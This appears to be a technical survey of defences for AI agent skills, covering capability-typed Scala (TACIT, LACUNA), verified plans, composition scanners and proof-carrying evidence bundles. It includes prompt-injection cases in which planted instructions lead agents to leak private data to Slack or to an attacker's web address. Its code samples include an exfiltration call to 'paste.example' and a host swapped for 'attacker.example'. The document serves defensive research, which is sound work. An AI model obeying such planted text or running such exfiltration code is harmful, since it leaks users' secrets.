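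Xie, Du and colleagues (2026), in *Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition*, counted harmful changes in a simulated environment rather than counting tool calls. In one set of tests, a read-only skill found a target and a second skill could act on it. The agent caused harm in 33.6% of trials when it had both skills and in almost none when it had only one. The low single-skill rate is partly a result of the test design, because each skill supplies only half of the attack.

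In another set of tests, a model's rate of risky approvals rose from 15.7% to 27.0% when it had access to a skill's advisory notes. The model treated findings in the notes, such as "the risk is acceptable", as authorization. An operator who uses a language model as the broker therefore has to keep such notes out of its input or make clear that they carry no authority.

### Two leaks between public skills

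*Scan Before You Install* (Gandhi, Aviv and colleagues, 2026) reports finding combinations of this kind in popular public skills. Its scanner builds a graph with a node for each skill. It draws an edge when one skill writes a file or environment variable that another reads, or when one skill invokes another by name. Further rules and a language model can add edges for data passed through the conversation. The scanner then searches for dangerous paths, such as one from a skill that reads sensitive data to one that sends data out.

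Before reporting an unauthorized interaction, a language model has to quote evidence for four claims:

- the sending skill produces the data;
- the receiving skill uses it;
- the agent can pass it on without the user choosing it;
- the result exceeds what the user authorized.

In October 2026, the researchers reported two such leaks among 1,587 skills from the 75 most-starred GitHub repositories that contain skills. The scanner had checked the four skills involved individually and found nothing wrong.

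One leak involved two skills, one that searches the agent's past conversations and one that posts to Slack. The researchers prepared a stored conversation containing a private pricing decision, a fake billing key, and a GitHub issue the agent had read, which had an instruction hidden in a comment. When the agent later searched its history, it read the hidden instruction again. With shell commands approved in advance, GPT-5.2-Codex made an unauthorized Slack request in 2 of 12 runs, and GLM-5 followed the instruction in 7 of 12.

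In the other leak, a feed monitor displayed an item containing an attacker's web address. The agent passed the address to a diagnostic skill, which sent its stored access token there. This happened in 5 of 12 runs with GPT-5.2-Codex and 6 of 12 with GLM-5. Newer models may resist these instructions more often, but the runs show that the paths work.

Metere's three methods would permit the Slack leak. Suppose one manifest declares reading the conversation history and the other declares `publish(slack)`. Both calls are then within *D*, and from the "declared" level upwards the runtime posts the message without asking for approval. Gandhi and colleagues instead recommend replacing the Slack skill with one whose send tool has its own permission, separate from the shell's, so that the user can require approval for every message. Of the eight alternatives they considered, this was the only one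 that both ran on the user's agent and enforced approval outside the model's instructions.

The scanner can't prove that a set of skills is safe. The conversation reader and the Slack skill share no file or variable, and only the language model proposed the edge between them. In a test on 485 sets of skills, the fixed rules found 54.7% of the risky sets and flagged no harmless ones. With the model's proposals and the evidence check, the scanner found 95.4% of the risky ones and wrongly flagged 2.4% of the harmless ones.

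### Restricting what the agent may send after reading a secret

Metere's confidentiality labels could stop both the password leak and the Slack leak, although the composition theorem does not use them. Combining two pieces of data gives the result the higher of their ranks, and data may not go to a recipient with a lower rank. If the runtime applied this rule to the whole session, reading a file marked "restricted" would raise the session's rank, and the gate would block anything sent to a public website. The label has to apply to the whole session because separate labels for each skill would not track data that the model carries from one skill to another.

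The operator would have to label every sensitive file correctly. The rule would also block harmless requests, so an agent that had read one restricted file could no longer look up an exchange rate. Metere lists how to lower labels safely as an open problem. A type system can be more precise by tracking individual values instead of the whole session.

### Which method stops which attack

The table assumes the repaired theorem, in which *D* includes targets and the gate denies every undeclared call.

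| Attack | Method that stops it | Premise | What remains |
|---|---|---|---|
| A script contacts an undeclared host | static analysis | the analyser covers libraries, redirects and code loaded at run time | harmful use of declared hosts |
| The model requests an undeclared payment | typed dispatch | every host call passes through dispatch | the denied request, and harmful arguments to declared tools |
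| A registered tool has an undeclared effect | none | – | the effect, unless the operator analyses or sandboxes the tool |
| An extension acts without using the gate | none; the run-time check may detect it afterwards | the runtime monitors the object, and the log is accurate | the effect itself, if irreversible |
| One permitted call reads a secret and another sends it | none | – | the leak, unless labels or a required approval stop it |
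| The model reveals a secret in a message | none; the text scanner may block it | the secret matches a known pattern | paraphrased secrets |
| The world changes after approval | none; the run-time check may detect it afterwards | the change affects the operation or target | changes to content |
| Someone coerces the operator | none | – | approval of a harmful request or an overly broad manifest |

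## Type-checking the code and plans an agent writes

The password in the previous section leaked because the runtime checked each call separately, while the data passed from one call to the other inside the model's context. An agent can instead submit the whole sequence of calls as a short program. A compiler can then trace the data through the program and reject the program before any of it runs, which is earlier than typed dispatch can reject an envelope.

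### Capabilities in types

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a server that takes Scala 3 programs from an agent and runs those that compile. In Metere's manifest a capability is a name, but in Scala it is a value in the program, such as an open file or a network connection. Code can use the file only if it can reach that value.

Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, records in each type which capabilities a value can reach. If `f` is a file, the function `(s: String) => f.write(s)` has the type

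`String ->{f} Unit`.

A function of type `String ->{f} Unit` takes a string, returns nothing useful and may use `f`. The part in braces, `{f}`, is the capture set. Like the result of a sound static analysis, it may list more than the function uses but never less. A function of type `String -> Unit` is called pure. Its capture set is empty, so it cannot write a file, contact a server or print.

A function can use these types to limit the code that others pass to it. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)*, give this example, in which `net` is a network and `fs` a file system:

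```scala
def run(task: () ->{net} Unit) = task()
run(() => net.send(fs.read("secret")))
```

The compiler rejects the second line because the function passed to `run` uses `fs` as well as `net`.

Types also limit how long a capability lasts. TACIT grants access to a folder only inside a block of code, and the compiler rejects a block that would return the access, even wrapped in a function or a list.

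### A secret the agent can use but not send

In TACIT, the operator marks some folders as classified. When a program reads a file there, it receives a `Classified[String]`, a wrapper around the text. The program can work on the text only through the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts only pure functions and wraps the result again.

Suppose the notes folder from the earlier leak is classified. The compiler accepts this program:

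```scala
val notes = requestFileSystem("/home/ana/notes") {
  readClassified("/home/ana/notes/servers.txt")
}
println(notes.map(text => text.length))
```

The function inside `map` only computes a length, so it is pure. The wrapped text may leave the block because it is data and gives no access to the folder. `println` shows the length in the user's terminal and sends `Classified(****)` to the agent.

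A planted instruction now leads the agent to submit a second program:

```scala
requestNetwork(Set("paste.example")) {
  notes.map(text => httpPost("https://paste.example/new", text))
}
```

`httpPost` needs the network capability, so the function inside `map` has that capability in its capture set. `map` requires an empty capture set, so the compiler rejects the program for a type mismatch before it can contact any server. Passing `notes` directly to `httpPost` also fails, because `httpPost` expects an ordinary string. If the program first converts `notes` to a string, it compiles but sends only the asterisks.

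To summarise a classified document, the agent's program can pass it to a separate language model that the operator trusts, usually one on the user's own machine. The answer comes back wrapped, and the cloud model that runs the agent never receives the text.

*SPA* (2026) describes a run-time alternative called FIDES, which labels the agent's context with the combined labels of everything the agent has read and checks each tool call against that label. Like the session-wide label discussed earlier, it can block harmless requests. TACIT avoids this problem because the secret never enters the context.

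*SPA* also distinguishes confidentiality from integrity, which concerns whether untrusted data influences an action. TACIT's types mainly protect confidentiality, so an instruction planted in an ordinary file can still change what the agent tries to do, within the access its programs can obtain.

### Safe mode and the trusted parts

Ordinary Scala code can bypass its type system. A programmer can use a cast to declare an impure function pure. A program can also use reflection to look up a method by name while it runs, so the compiler cannot determine which method it will call. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's code in safe mode, which forbids unchecked casts, reflection and annotations that suppress compiler checks. Safe mode also limits the code to libraries that satisfy the same rules or that a programmer has marked as safe after checking them by other means.

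The guarantee depends on the compiler, TACIT's own library, the software that runs the compiled code, and the trusted model. Researchers have proved that the basic type system is sound and checked the proofs by computer, but Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet proved that safe mode has the properties they need.

TACIT handles exceptions at run time. Almost any code can fail, for example by dividing by zero, and the error message could contain part of a secret. TACIT catches the exception and uses Scala's standard `Try` type to turn it into an ordinary value, which it can wrap like other classified data.

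Pham and colleagues found that the earlier type of `Try` wrongly described the result as pure, since reading it can rethrow the stored exception. The error concerned the right to throw exceptions, not access to files, but it shows how a library can misdescribe its own effects. They corrected it by sorting capabilities into kinds, so that the type of `Try` keeps only those related to control flow, and proved the extended system safe in Lean 4 for a small model of the language. The share of standard library lines that pass capture checking rose from 66.7% to 81.7%, partly because of other changes.

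The library also checks folders and hosts at run time. A function's type shows that it uses a network, but the library compares the address with the list of permitted hosts only when the program makes the request. In the examples above, the agent's own program supplies that list. To enforce a skill's manifest, the library would have to compare each requested folder and host with *D* before granting access.

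Two other gaps remain. A function inside `map` can run longer if the password starts with a certain letter, and the agent can learn something from the delay. A program may also start external commands, which Scala's rules don't cover. If the operator permits `cat`, a command that prints files, the agent can use it to read the secret without a wrapper. TACIT has a strict setting that blocks such commands, but it is off by default, and a permitted Python interpreter could also read the secret.

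### The leakage tests

Odersky and colleagues gave two agents a software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted instructions, for 120 trials. In 11 further trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or pretended to have authority to see them. They ran each trial once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as ordinary strings. A trial counted as a leak if secret text appeared in the agent's output.

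| Model | Type of trial | Leaks, wrapped | Leaks, ordinary strings |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | planted instruction | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | malicious user | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | planted instruction | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | malicious user | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

The zeros follow from the types, so these trials mainly test whether the implementation matches the theory. A search for secret text would not detect a leak through timing. The wrapper did not stop useful work. One agent completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with it and 83.3% without it, and the other completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. The researchers suspect that Sonnet scored lower without the wrapper because of the test's time limits and because Sonnet tends to stop to warn the user.

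They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, the benchmark used to test NOMOS. One attack in 1,926 trials counted as successful. The agent had booked the right hotel but quoted reviews in which the attacker had recommended another, and the benchmark checks only for that other hotel's name.

TACIT's completion rate on harmless AgentDojo tasks was less impressive. Odersky and colleagues call it comparable to that of CaMeL, which tracks the origin of data while a program runs, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks against CaMeL's 81.4%, and 47.6% of the Slack tasks against 68.6%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the two systems' scores were closer, except in travel, where TACIT completed 64.3% of the tasks and CaMeL 1.4%.

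### The cost of writing Scala

The researchers tested whether typed code makes agents less capable by comparing it with ordinary tool calls on the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, running each task ten times.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
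| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

The agents did slightly better in Scala, which the researchers attribute to clearer data types and helpful error messages. At most 8% of the programs needed correcting, and those usually needed only one correction. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% of them in Scala and 43.3% with its usual tools.

None of the customer-service tools returned classified data, so the τ²-bench results measure how much writing Scala hinders the agent, but not how much hiding data from it does. The AgentDojo results are a better guide to the effect of hiding data.

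### Variables in scope as permissions

TACIT leaves the agent's main loop unchanged and checks the programs the agent submits. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) puts the model's code inside a larger program. A developer writes `agent[T](task)` wherever the program needs a value of type `T`. When the program reaches that point, the model writes code for the task, and the compiler checks it as if the developer had written it there.

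Take a function that converts a budget into euros:

```scala
def total(rates: RateService^, budget: String): Double =
  agent[Double]("convert the budget to euros and add it up")
```

The model's code can use `rates` and `budget` because they are in scope. If the developer has put no payment function in scope, the compiler rejects code that calls one because the name is undefined. The function's parameters therefore work much like a manifest, although the code can also use any definitions visible to the whole file.

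Capture checking is optional in LACUNA, but the permissions are reliable only when it is on. The developer also needs safe mode, because otherwise the code can use reflection or start an external program.

The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, the model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return a number. It writes a correct subtraction followed by a line that returns text. The compiler rejects both lines, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again. Python would run the subtraction before reaching the faulty line. Code that passes the check can still stop halfway, for example when a server fails, so the crash problem from the section on model checking remains.

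Unlike TACIT, LACUNA solved fewer τ²-bench tasks overall than ordinary tool calling did. Zhao and colleagues ran 392 tasks. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% and ordinary tool calling solved 90.0%, though they describe the two as on par. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the figures were 29.1% and 33.2%. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's programs in the retail tasks and 89% of Gemini's in the telecom tasks. Rejection keeps a program from doing harm, but the agent makes no progress if it can't write valid Scala.

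On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded. Zhao and colleagues explain that the types cannot stop a manipulated model from misusing a capability that the task needs, or one that the developer granted unnecessarily. This is the same problem as harmful arguments to permitted tools.

### Verifying a plan before the first tool call

Many rules concern the order of actions rather than access to data. In *SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026), the agent writes a plan in a small Python-like language, and Dafny verifies the plan before the agent calls any tool. Dafny turns claims about a program into formulas for an SMT solver.

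An airline's policy allows an agent to cancel a booking only if the customer has not yet flown any part of it. A further rule, in this simplified version, limits cancellation to the first 24 hours. The planner proposes:

```
LOOKUP:       resv = call(Get-Resv, rid)              then CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE:    hrs = call(Hours-Diff, resv.ts, time)   then CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES:  if hrs <= 24 then DO_CANCEL, else NOT_PERMITTED
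DO_CANCEL:    call(Cancel-Resv, rid, reason)          then DONE
```

Each tool has a contract, which consists of a precondition on its inputs and a postcondition on its result. Let Σ(*s*) describe everything the verifier knows when the plan reaches step *s*. This includes the postconditions of earlier calls and the outcomes of earlier tests. Soteria has Dafny check three properties:

- **Tool preconditions.** If step *s* calls tool *a* with inputs *v* under the condition *g*, then Σ(*s*) ∧ *g* must imply *a*'s precondition for *v*.
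- **Progress.** Some possible execution must reach each step, and at least one way forward must always be open. At CHECK_RULES, `hrs` is either at most 24 or more than 24, so the plan can't get stuck.
- **Policy compliance.** The verifier keeps an imaginary log of the plan's calls. At the end of every path, the log must satisfy every rule in the policy.

The plan fails the last check because it never calls `No-Flown`. The policy requires that for every call to `Cancel-Resv`, the log contains an earlier call to `No-Flown` that returned "true" for the same booking. Dafny reports the broken rule, and the planner adds the missing step before the booking changes.

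Soteria also records which tool results contributed to each variable. A rule can therefore require a refund amount to come from the booking record, so that the model cannot invent it.

The planner gets up to eight retries. To simplify planning, He and colleagues prepared verified sub-plans for common procedures such as cancellation. A larger plan can call these sub-plans like tools. In one test, 65 of 68 plans passed with sub-plans, compared with 38 of 60 without them. The method does not accept plans with loops, and the proof assumes that every tool fulfils its contract.

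### How much of Soteria's result comes from the proof

He and colleagues tested Soteria with four models on 207 tasks from τ²-bench and Toolathlon, a benchmark of longer office and file tasks. It broke none of the formal rules, while the best alternative system kept to them in at most 93% of tasks. But Soteria also has a monitor that checks every tool call during the session. The researchers added the components one at a time on the airline tasks:

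| Configuration | Tasks without a violation, GPT-5.4-mini | Tasks without a violation, Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| unverified plan | 74% | 54% |
| verified plan | 80% | 56% |
| verified plan with sub-plans | 80% | 58% |
| the same, with the run-time monitor | 100% | 100% |

Verification alone helped little because the agent could depart from its plan and sometimes did. Soteria's strict mode permits only planned calls, but it also blocks harmless unplanned ones, such as looking up a second booking at the user's request. The 100% result is expected, since the monitor enforces the same rules the researchers used to count violations. They also corrected some rules and added others while auditing the results.

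The plan probably helps mainly by guiding the agent when the monitor blocks a call. With Claude Opus 4.6, Soteria completed 88.0% of airline tasks and 90.4% of retail tasks without a violation, compared with 56.0% and 46.5% for the best alternatives. The advantage was less certain with GPT-5.4-mini. Across five runs of the airline tasks with only three planning retries, Soteria averaged 50.8% and the rule-based monitor AgentSpec averaged 48.0%, with overlapping confidence intervals.

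On Toolathlon, Soteria with Opus completed 18.6% of tasks. Opus with no guard completed 30.2%, but only 11.6% without breaking a rule. Planning also makes long conversations more expensive, because the agent makes a new plan at each turn. An airline task with Opus cost about $0.80 with Soteria and $0.32 without it.

### Compared with checking each envelope

| | Typed dispatch | TACIT and LACUNA | Soteria |
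|---|---|---|---|
| What a tool checks in advance | the runtime's code | each program the agent writes | each plan the agent writes |
| What has to change | the dispatch function and its callers | tools need Scala interfaces, and the agent writes Scala | tools need contracts, and the agent writes plans |
| Who sets the limits | the skill's author, in the manifest | the operator or the developer of the surrounding program | the operator, starting from a model's draft |
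| What remains for run time | the test of every envelope | hosts, paths, exceptions and external commands | departures from the plan |

Typed dispatch requires the least change to the agent, which sends the same envelopes as before. TACIT's shared library has about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the interfaces for each group of tools add a few hundred more. Much of this interface code repeats the existing tool descriptions, so an agent can draft it for a person to review.

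Soteria's rules take more judgment to write. He et al. wrote 24 for the airline, 33 for the retailer and 41 for Toolathlon, spending a few hours on each set. Dafny can prove that a plan obeys these rules, but it cannot detect a missing rule. An operator with skills from many fields would need a separate set for each field.

None of these systems verifies the Python and shell scripts that skills already contain. TACIT can run such a script as an external command, but its types do not cover what the script then does. Soteria can treat the script as a tool, but someone has to write its contract, and the verifier assumes the script obeys it. Zhao and colleagues note that their guarantees do not carry over to Python, the language of most agent software, because Python has no static types to enforce them.

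Developers who let agents write Python can still screen the code. *SpatialClaw* (2026) describes an agent whose code passes through two filters before it runs. The first checks the parsed program for file access, network access and constructs such as `eval`, and the second searches the text for the names of methods that write files. These filters stop many mistakes, but they have the same weakness as the pattern-based skill scanners.

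A skill without scripts fits TACIT better, because the agent can read SKILL.md and write Scala to follow it. Most published skills appear to have no scripts, although many involve shell commands, which may need Scala replacements. If a script is too long to rewrite, the operator could run it in a sandbox without network access and give it a Scala interface that returns its output as `Classified`. The compiler would then control where the output goes, while the sandbox would have to keep the script from sending anything itself.

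## Evidence bundles and the re-check when a skill is loaded

TACIT, LACUNA and Soteria check an agent's code on the machine that will run it. A skill's author can instead analyse the scripts before publishing them and ship the results, but the operator then needs a reason to trust them. Metere's solution is the evidence bundle, a set of files that the runtime re-checks when it loads the skill.

### Proof-carrying code

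The bundle is modelled on an idea from Necula's *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997), which considers how a computer can safely run machine code from a stranger. A signature shows who produced the code, but even a trusted person can make mistakes or act maliciously. Necula therefore has the producer ship a proof that the code is safe. Finding the proof may take extensive analysis or human help, but checking it is quick.

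The method has five steps:

1. The consumer, who will run the code, publishes a safety policy that lists the permitted operations and their conditions.
2. The producer attaches an invariant to each loop, which is a statement that holds every time the program reaches that point.
3. A program called a verification condition generator turns the code, the invariants and the policy into a formula. If the formula is true, the code obeys the policy.
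4. The producer proves the formula and ships the proof with the code and the invariants.
5. The consumer generates the formula again from the code it received and checks the proof against it. If the proof is valid, the code can run without further checks.

Necula's example is an assembly-language function that sums a list of integers. The policy lets it read only valid memory and requires it to return an integer. The loop's invariant is that one register holds a list and another holds an integer. The formula then has two parts: (1) the invariant holds when the loop begins, and (2) if it holds before a pass, every memory access in that pass is permitted, and afterwards either the invariant holds again or the function returns an integer. Finding good invariants is often the hardest part of a proof, and the producer has already done it.

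If an attacker changes the function to read other memory, the consumer's generator produces a different formula, which the shipped proof does not prove. If the attacker also supplies a valid proof of the new formula, the new code obeys the policy. Tampering is therefore "either detected or harmless", as Necula puts it, and the method needs no signatures.

The consumer still has to trust the policy, the generator and the proof checker. Necula's checker is small, since a simple version of its rules takes a couple of pages of code. The IMDEA Software Institute calls the proofs shipped in such systems "certificates".

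### Java's stack maps and the Linux eBPF verifier

Necula doubted that this way of finding proofs would scale to realistic programs, and expected compilers to generate the proofs as they translated the code. Java compilers do this for one simple property. Before a Java virtual machine runs a program, it checks that no instruction uses a value of the wrong type, such as an integer where the instruction needs an object reference. According to *Understanding The StackMapTable Method Attribute* (stevenlwcz, 2025), before Java 6 the machine inferred the types at every instruction itself, which was slow.

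Java compilers now ship a table of stack maps with the code. Each entry gives the types of the local variables and temporary values at one instruction. A draft of the Java standard (OpenJDK, 2026) requires an entry for every jump target. The Java virtual machine goes through the code once, working out the types from one entry to the next and comparing them with the table. A wrong entry causes an error, so the check does not depend on the compiler being correct.

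Linux has no such table for eBPF programs, which users load into the operating system's kernel to filter network traffic, for example. The kernel's verifier analyses each program when it is loaded. It follows the possible paths, tracks the type and range of each value, and rejects the program if it cannot rule out an unsafe memory access. Authors do not have to supply a proof, but the kernel has to contain a complete analyser. That analyser is large, and bugs in it have let attackers take control of the kernel. The verifier also limits how many instructions it examines, so it rejects some safe programs as too complex.

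### The four files

Metere specifies four files. The bundles that enclawed produces have the same structure, but weaker contents.

| File | Contents in the design | Contents in enclawed |
|---|---|---|
| `static.json` | the effects of each script, with the analyser's name, version and a hash of its rules | the pattern scanner's result |
| `types.proof` | the type checker's proof or, for TypeScript, the set of modules the compiler accepted | the result of trying the dispatcher on every capability name |
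| `smt.unsat` | the solver's formula and, where available, its certificate | the enumerator's verdict, with a hash of *D* and *K* |
| `manifest.attest.json` | a signed statement that the manifest has reached the formal level, with hashes of the other three files and the names of the tools | the same |

A hash is a short code computed from a file, which in practice changes whenever the file does.

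Only `static.json` contains evidence about the skill's own programs. The dispatch function and the gate belong to the operator's runtime, which the skill's author may never have seen. A proof about one version of the dispatch function does not cover the next version, so the operator could verify both components once for each runtime release instead of receiving new evidence about them with every skill.

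### The five steps of the re-check

1. The runtime verifies the signature on the manifest and the skill's content.
2. It verifies the signed statement in `manifest.attest.json` and confirms that the signer may vouch for the formal level.
3. It analyses the scripts again, checks that their effects lie within *D*, and compares the result with `static.json`.
4. It checks the dispatch function against *D* again.
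5. It runs the bounded search again. If the bundle contains a solver's certificate, a separate checker examines it.

| Step | What the operator trusts | What the runtime recomputes | Tampering it catches |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | the list of trusted keys | the signature check on the skill | edits to the manifest, SKILL.md or a script after signing |
| 2 | the record of who may vouch for which level | the signature check on the statement | a forged statement, or one from a signer without authority |
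| 3 | the analyser and its table of library effects | the effects of every script | a false `static.json`, or a script with new effects that the analyser can find |
| 4 | the type checker or, in enclawed, the test of the dispatcher | the check of dispatch | a false `types.proof` |
| 5 | the solver or enumerator, and the model of the gate | the search | a false verdict |

Step 1 works only if the runtime recomputes the hashes from the files on disk. In a demonstration by the vendor AgentLair, someone added one byte to a signed skill's README. The signature remained valid because it covered the skill's stored hash, which had not changed. The verifier detected the edit only when it hashed the files again.

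The five steps do not mention comparing the evidence files with the hashes in the signed statement, but enclawed's re-checker does this too.

### An edited script

The table uses the exchange-rate script analysed by hand earlier, with a manifest that permits both of its hosts and writing to `./rates/`. It shows four ways of editing the script after someone has produced the bundle. An insider here is someone with a key that the runtime accepts for formal skills.

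| Edit | Who makes it | Result |
|---|---|---|
| replace the backup host with `attacker.example` | an intruder without a key | step 1 fails |
| the same | an insider, who signs the skill again | step 3 fails |
| double every exchange rate | an insider | all steps pass |
| send data through a library function that the scanner does not recognise | an insider | all steps pass in enclawed |

When the insider adds `attacker.example`, step 2 still succeeds because the signed statement covers the manifest and the evidence files, which have not changed. Step 3 finds a network request outside *D*.

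Doubling the exchange rates does not change the script's effects, so step 3 reproduces `static.json` exactly. Containment still holds, and the edit is harmless in Necula's sense because the policy does not mention exchange rates. But the signed statement now accompanies a script that the signer may never have examined. Metere could prevent this by including a hash of every skill file in the statement.

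In the last case, a sound analyser would stop the skill at step 3, but enclawed's scanner reports the same effects as before. Steps 4 and 5 do not examine the script, so the skill loads at the formal level even though it exceeds its permissions. Only the signature, not the proof, would have stopped an intruder from making the same edit.

### A cache instead of a proof

Metere describes the re-check as "the precise structure of proof-carrying code" because the runtime does not rely on any of the producer's claims. Necula also intended the consumer to do much less work than the producer, which is mostly not the case here. The runtime repeats the static analysis, the dispatch check and the bounded search, so it works more like the eBPF verifier than like a Java virtual machine.

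Metere calls `static.json` a cache that the runtime can compare with its own result. Unlike a normal cache, it saves no work, because the runtime does the analysis anyway and the comparison is an extra step. If the runtime has found that *Ê*(*p*) ⊆ *D*, an old copy of *Ê*(*p*) adds nothing to the proof.

The comparison can also reject a good skill. Suppose the operator updates the analyser, and it now reports `api.example.com` where it used to report `*.example.com`. The new result is more precise and still lies within *D*, but it differs from `static.json`, so the runtime refuses to load the skill. The same can happen if the author used Semgrep and the operator's runtime has only enclawed's scanner. This undermines Metere's claim that the bundle is "portable by construction". A runtime could avoid the problem by treating a difference as a warning and rejecting the skill only if the new result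 goes beyond *D*.

Metere reports that the re-check could confirm Z3's result in milliseconds. That would be plausible if the runtime only checked a certificate, but step 5 also repeats the search. enclawed's enumerator produces no certificate, so it would have to go through all its sequences again each time a skill is loaded.

### A certificate for a fixpoint

The hand analysis of the exchange-rate script went through the loop until the summaries stopped changing. This stable result is called a fixpoint. The skill's author could ship it as a certificate, which the runtime could then confirm in one pass.

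Let *I* be the analyser's state when the program first reaches the loop, and let *F̂*(*S*) be the state after one pass that begins in state *S*. A claimed state *S* covers every pass if

*I* ⊑ *S* and *F̂*(*S*) ⊑ *S*.

The proof is by induction. *S* covers the state when execution first reaches the loop, and if it covers the state before a pass, it also covers the state after that pass.

For the exchange-rate script, the certificate would contain these claims about the top of the loop:

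| Claim | What the checker computes | Accepted? |
|---|---|---|
| `page` lies in [1, ∞) | [1, 1] on arrival and [2, ∞) after a pass, both within the claim | yes |
| `host` is one of the two names | one name from each branch before the loop, and no change inside it | yes |
| the effects are requests to the two hosts and writes to `rates/N.csv` | the same effects | yes |

If someone changes the claim about `page` to [1, 9], the checker finds that a pass through the loop can produce 10 and rejects the certificate. It also rejects the certificate if someone removes the backup host. A claim that is too broad passes this check, but the effects may no longer fit within *D*. Stack maps and Necula's loop invariants work on the same principle.

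The checker needs the transfer functions and the table of library effects, where most of the gaps in the earlier sections arose, but not widening, narrowing or a strategy for choosing which part of the program to analyse next. A certificate therefore makes the trusted part of the analyser smaller, but it does not add effects missing from the table.

The runtime would save very little time on a nine-line script. It could save more on a script that uses large libraries, because the author's analyser could summarise each library function and the runtime would confirm each summary once.

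### A certificate for an UNSAT verdict

Anyone can check a SAT answer by putting the solver's example into the formula, but an UNSAT answer has no example, so its certificate has to be a proof. For the earlier formula about an unapproved payment of more than 200 euros, the solver could ship this proof:

| Line | Statement | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | amount ≤ 150 or approved | given |
| 2 | not approved | given |
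| 3 | amount > 200 | given |
| 4 | amount ≤ 150 | lines 1 and 2 |
| 5 | contradiction | lines 3 and 4, by arithmetic |

The checker only has to confirm that each line follows from the lines it cites. It doesn't have to search for the next step, so it can be far simpler than the solver. Solvers for formulas with only true-or-false variables commonly write such proofs in the DRAT format, and some DRAT checkers have themselves been proved correct. Certificates from SMT solvers are more complicated because numbers, strings and arrays each need their own rules. A certificate can also be much longer than the formula it refutes.

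Metere suggests Z3's own proof-checking mode as the independent checker for step 5. That mode is part of the program it is supposed to check, so a separately written checker would provide better evidence.

The runtime also has to build the formula itself. Otherwise an attacker could supply a valid proof that some unrelated formula is unsatisfiable. In Necula's proof-carrying code, the consumer avoids this by generating the formula from the code it received.

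For the gate and the log, an invariant such as *w* = *ℓ* from the payment model would be a shorter certificate. It would also cover sessions of any length, while a certificate for *K* = 100 covers only sessions with up to 100 envelopes.

### A hash that leaves out the gate

The hash stored with the enumerator's verdict covers only *D* and *K*, so a re-checker can use it to confirm the bound but not to detect a change in the gate's policy. Suppose the gate denies every call outside *D* when the author produces the bundle, and the operator later lets a remote service approve such calls. The stored hash still matches because *D* and *K* have not changed, but the search examined the old policy.

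Repeating the search helps only if the enumerator reads the current policy, because an enumerator with a fixed model of the gate returns the old verdict. A better hash would also cover the gate's policy and source code, the model, the property and the checker version. A skill's author cannot know all of these for every operator, which is another reason to verify the gate with the runtime rather than with the skill.

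### When the re-check fails

Metere describes two different responses to a failure. If any step of the protocol fails, the runtime lowers the skill to "declared" and logs the reason. But step 3 aborts admission on a mismatch, and Metere later says that the load fails. In the paper on enclawed, a mismatch also aborts admission.

The choice matters because a skill lowered to "declared" would keep every automatic approval it had at the formal level. It would also lose the safeguard of comparing the log with the world at run time, which applies only at the "tested" level and above.

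Suppose step 3 detects that the exchange-rate script now contacts `attacker.example`. Lowering the skill to "declared" would not stop the attack, because the agent can still start the script and the script's network requests do not pass through the gate.

If the re-check finds a mismatch, refusing the skill is safer than lowering it to "unverified". Lowering it would restore the prompts for the model's irreversible calls but would not control the script's own network requests. If the check fails for a harmless reason, such as a missing solver, the operator could run the skill as unverified with its scripts in a sandbox.

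Java also has a fallback for class files of version 50. If the stack-map check fails, the virtual machine can still check the types by inferring them, which is slower. OpenJDK (2022) proposed removing this option for one kind of malformed entry. By contrast, a skill lowered to "declared" runs without the proof or a replacement for it.

### Keys and the choice of policy

In Metere's scheme, the skill's author writes *D*, whereas in proof-carrying code the consumer writes the safety policy. An attacker with a suitable key can therefore declare whatever a malicious script needs, and all five steps will succeed.

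Metere assumes that nobody steals the operator's key, and the limits on what each key may sign reduce the damage only from weaker ones. The operator could go further by setting a list *P* of capabilities that no skill may exceed. The runtime would then check

*Ê*(*p*) ⊆ *D* ⊆ *P*.

The author still describes what the skill needs, but a stolen key can no longer widen the limit.

Metere leaves revocation partly unsolved. If the operator withdraws a key while a skill signed with it is running, the runtime should remove the skill at the next gate event, but the design does not yet specify how.

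The list of keys also needs protection. enclawed's strict version locks the list at start-up, but the default open version allows changes afterwards, so an extension running in the same process could add its own key and sign a statement that passes step 2.

### The trusted toolchain

The analyser, the type checker and the solver may contain bugs. Metere proposes naming the trusted programs, auditing them once and reusing the audit. The bundle records their versions, and an operator may replace any of them with a formally verified equivalent. Metere gives the verified compiler CompCert as an example, but CompCert compiles C, and enclawed is written in JavaScript and TypeScript.

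Metere describes the bundle's verifier as a 350-line module. It calls the three analyses, so the operator also has to trust their code, the JavaScript engine and the signature library. Metere says the default tools are small enough to audit in an afternoon. However, they include a text scanner that misses effects.

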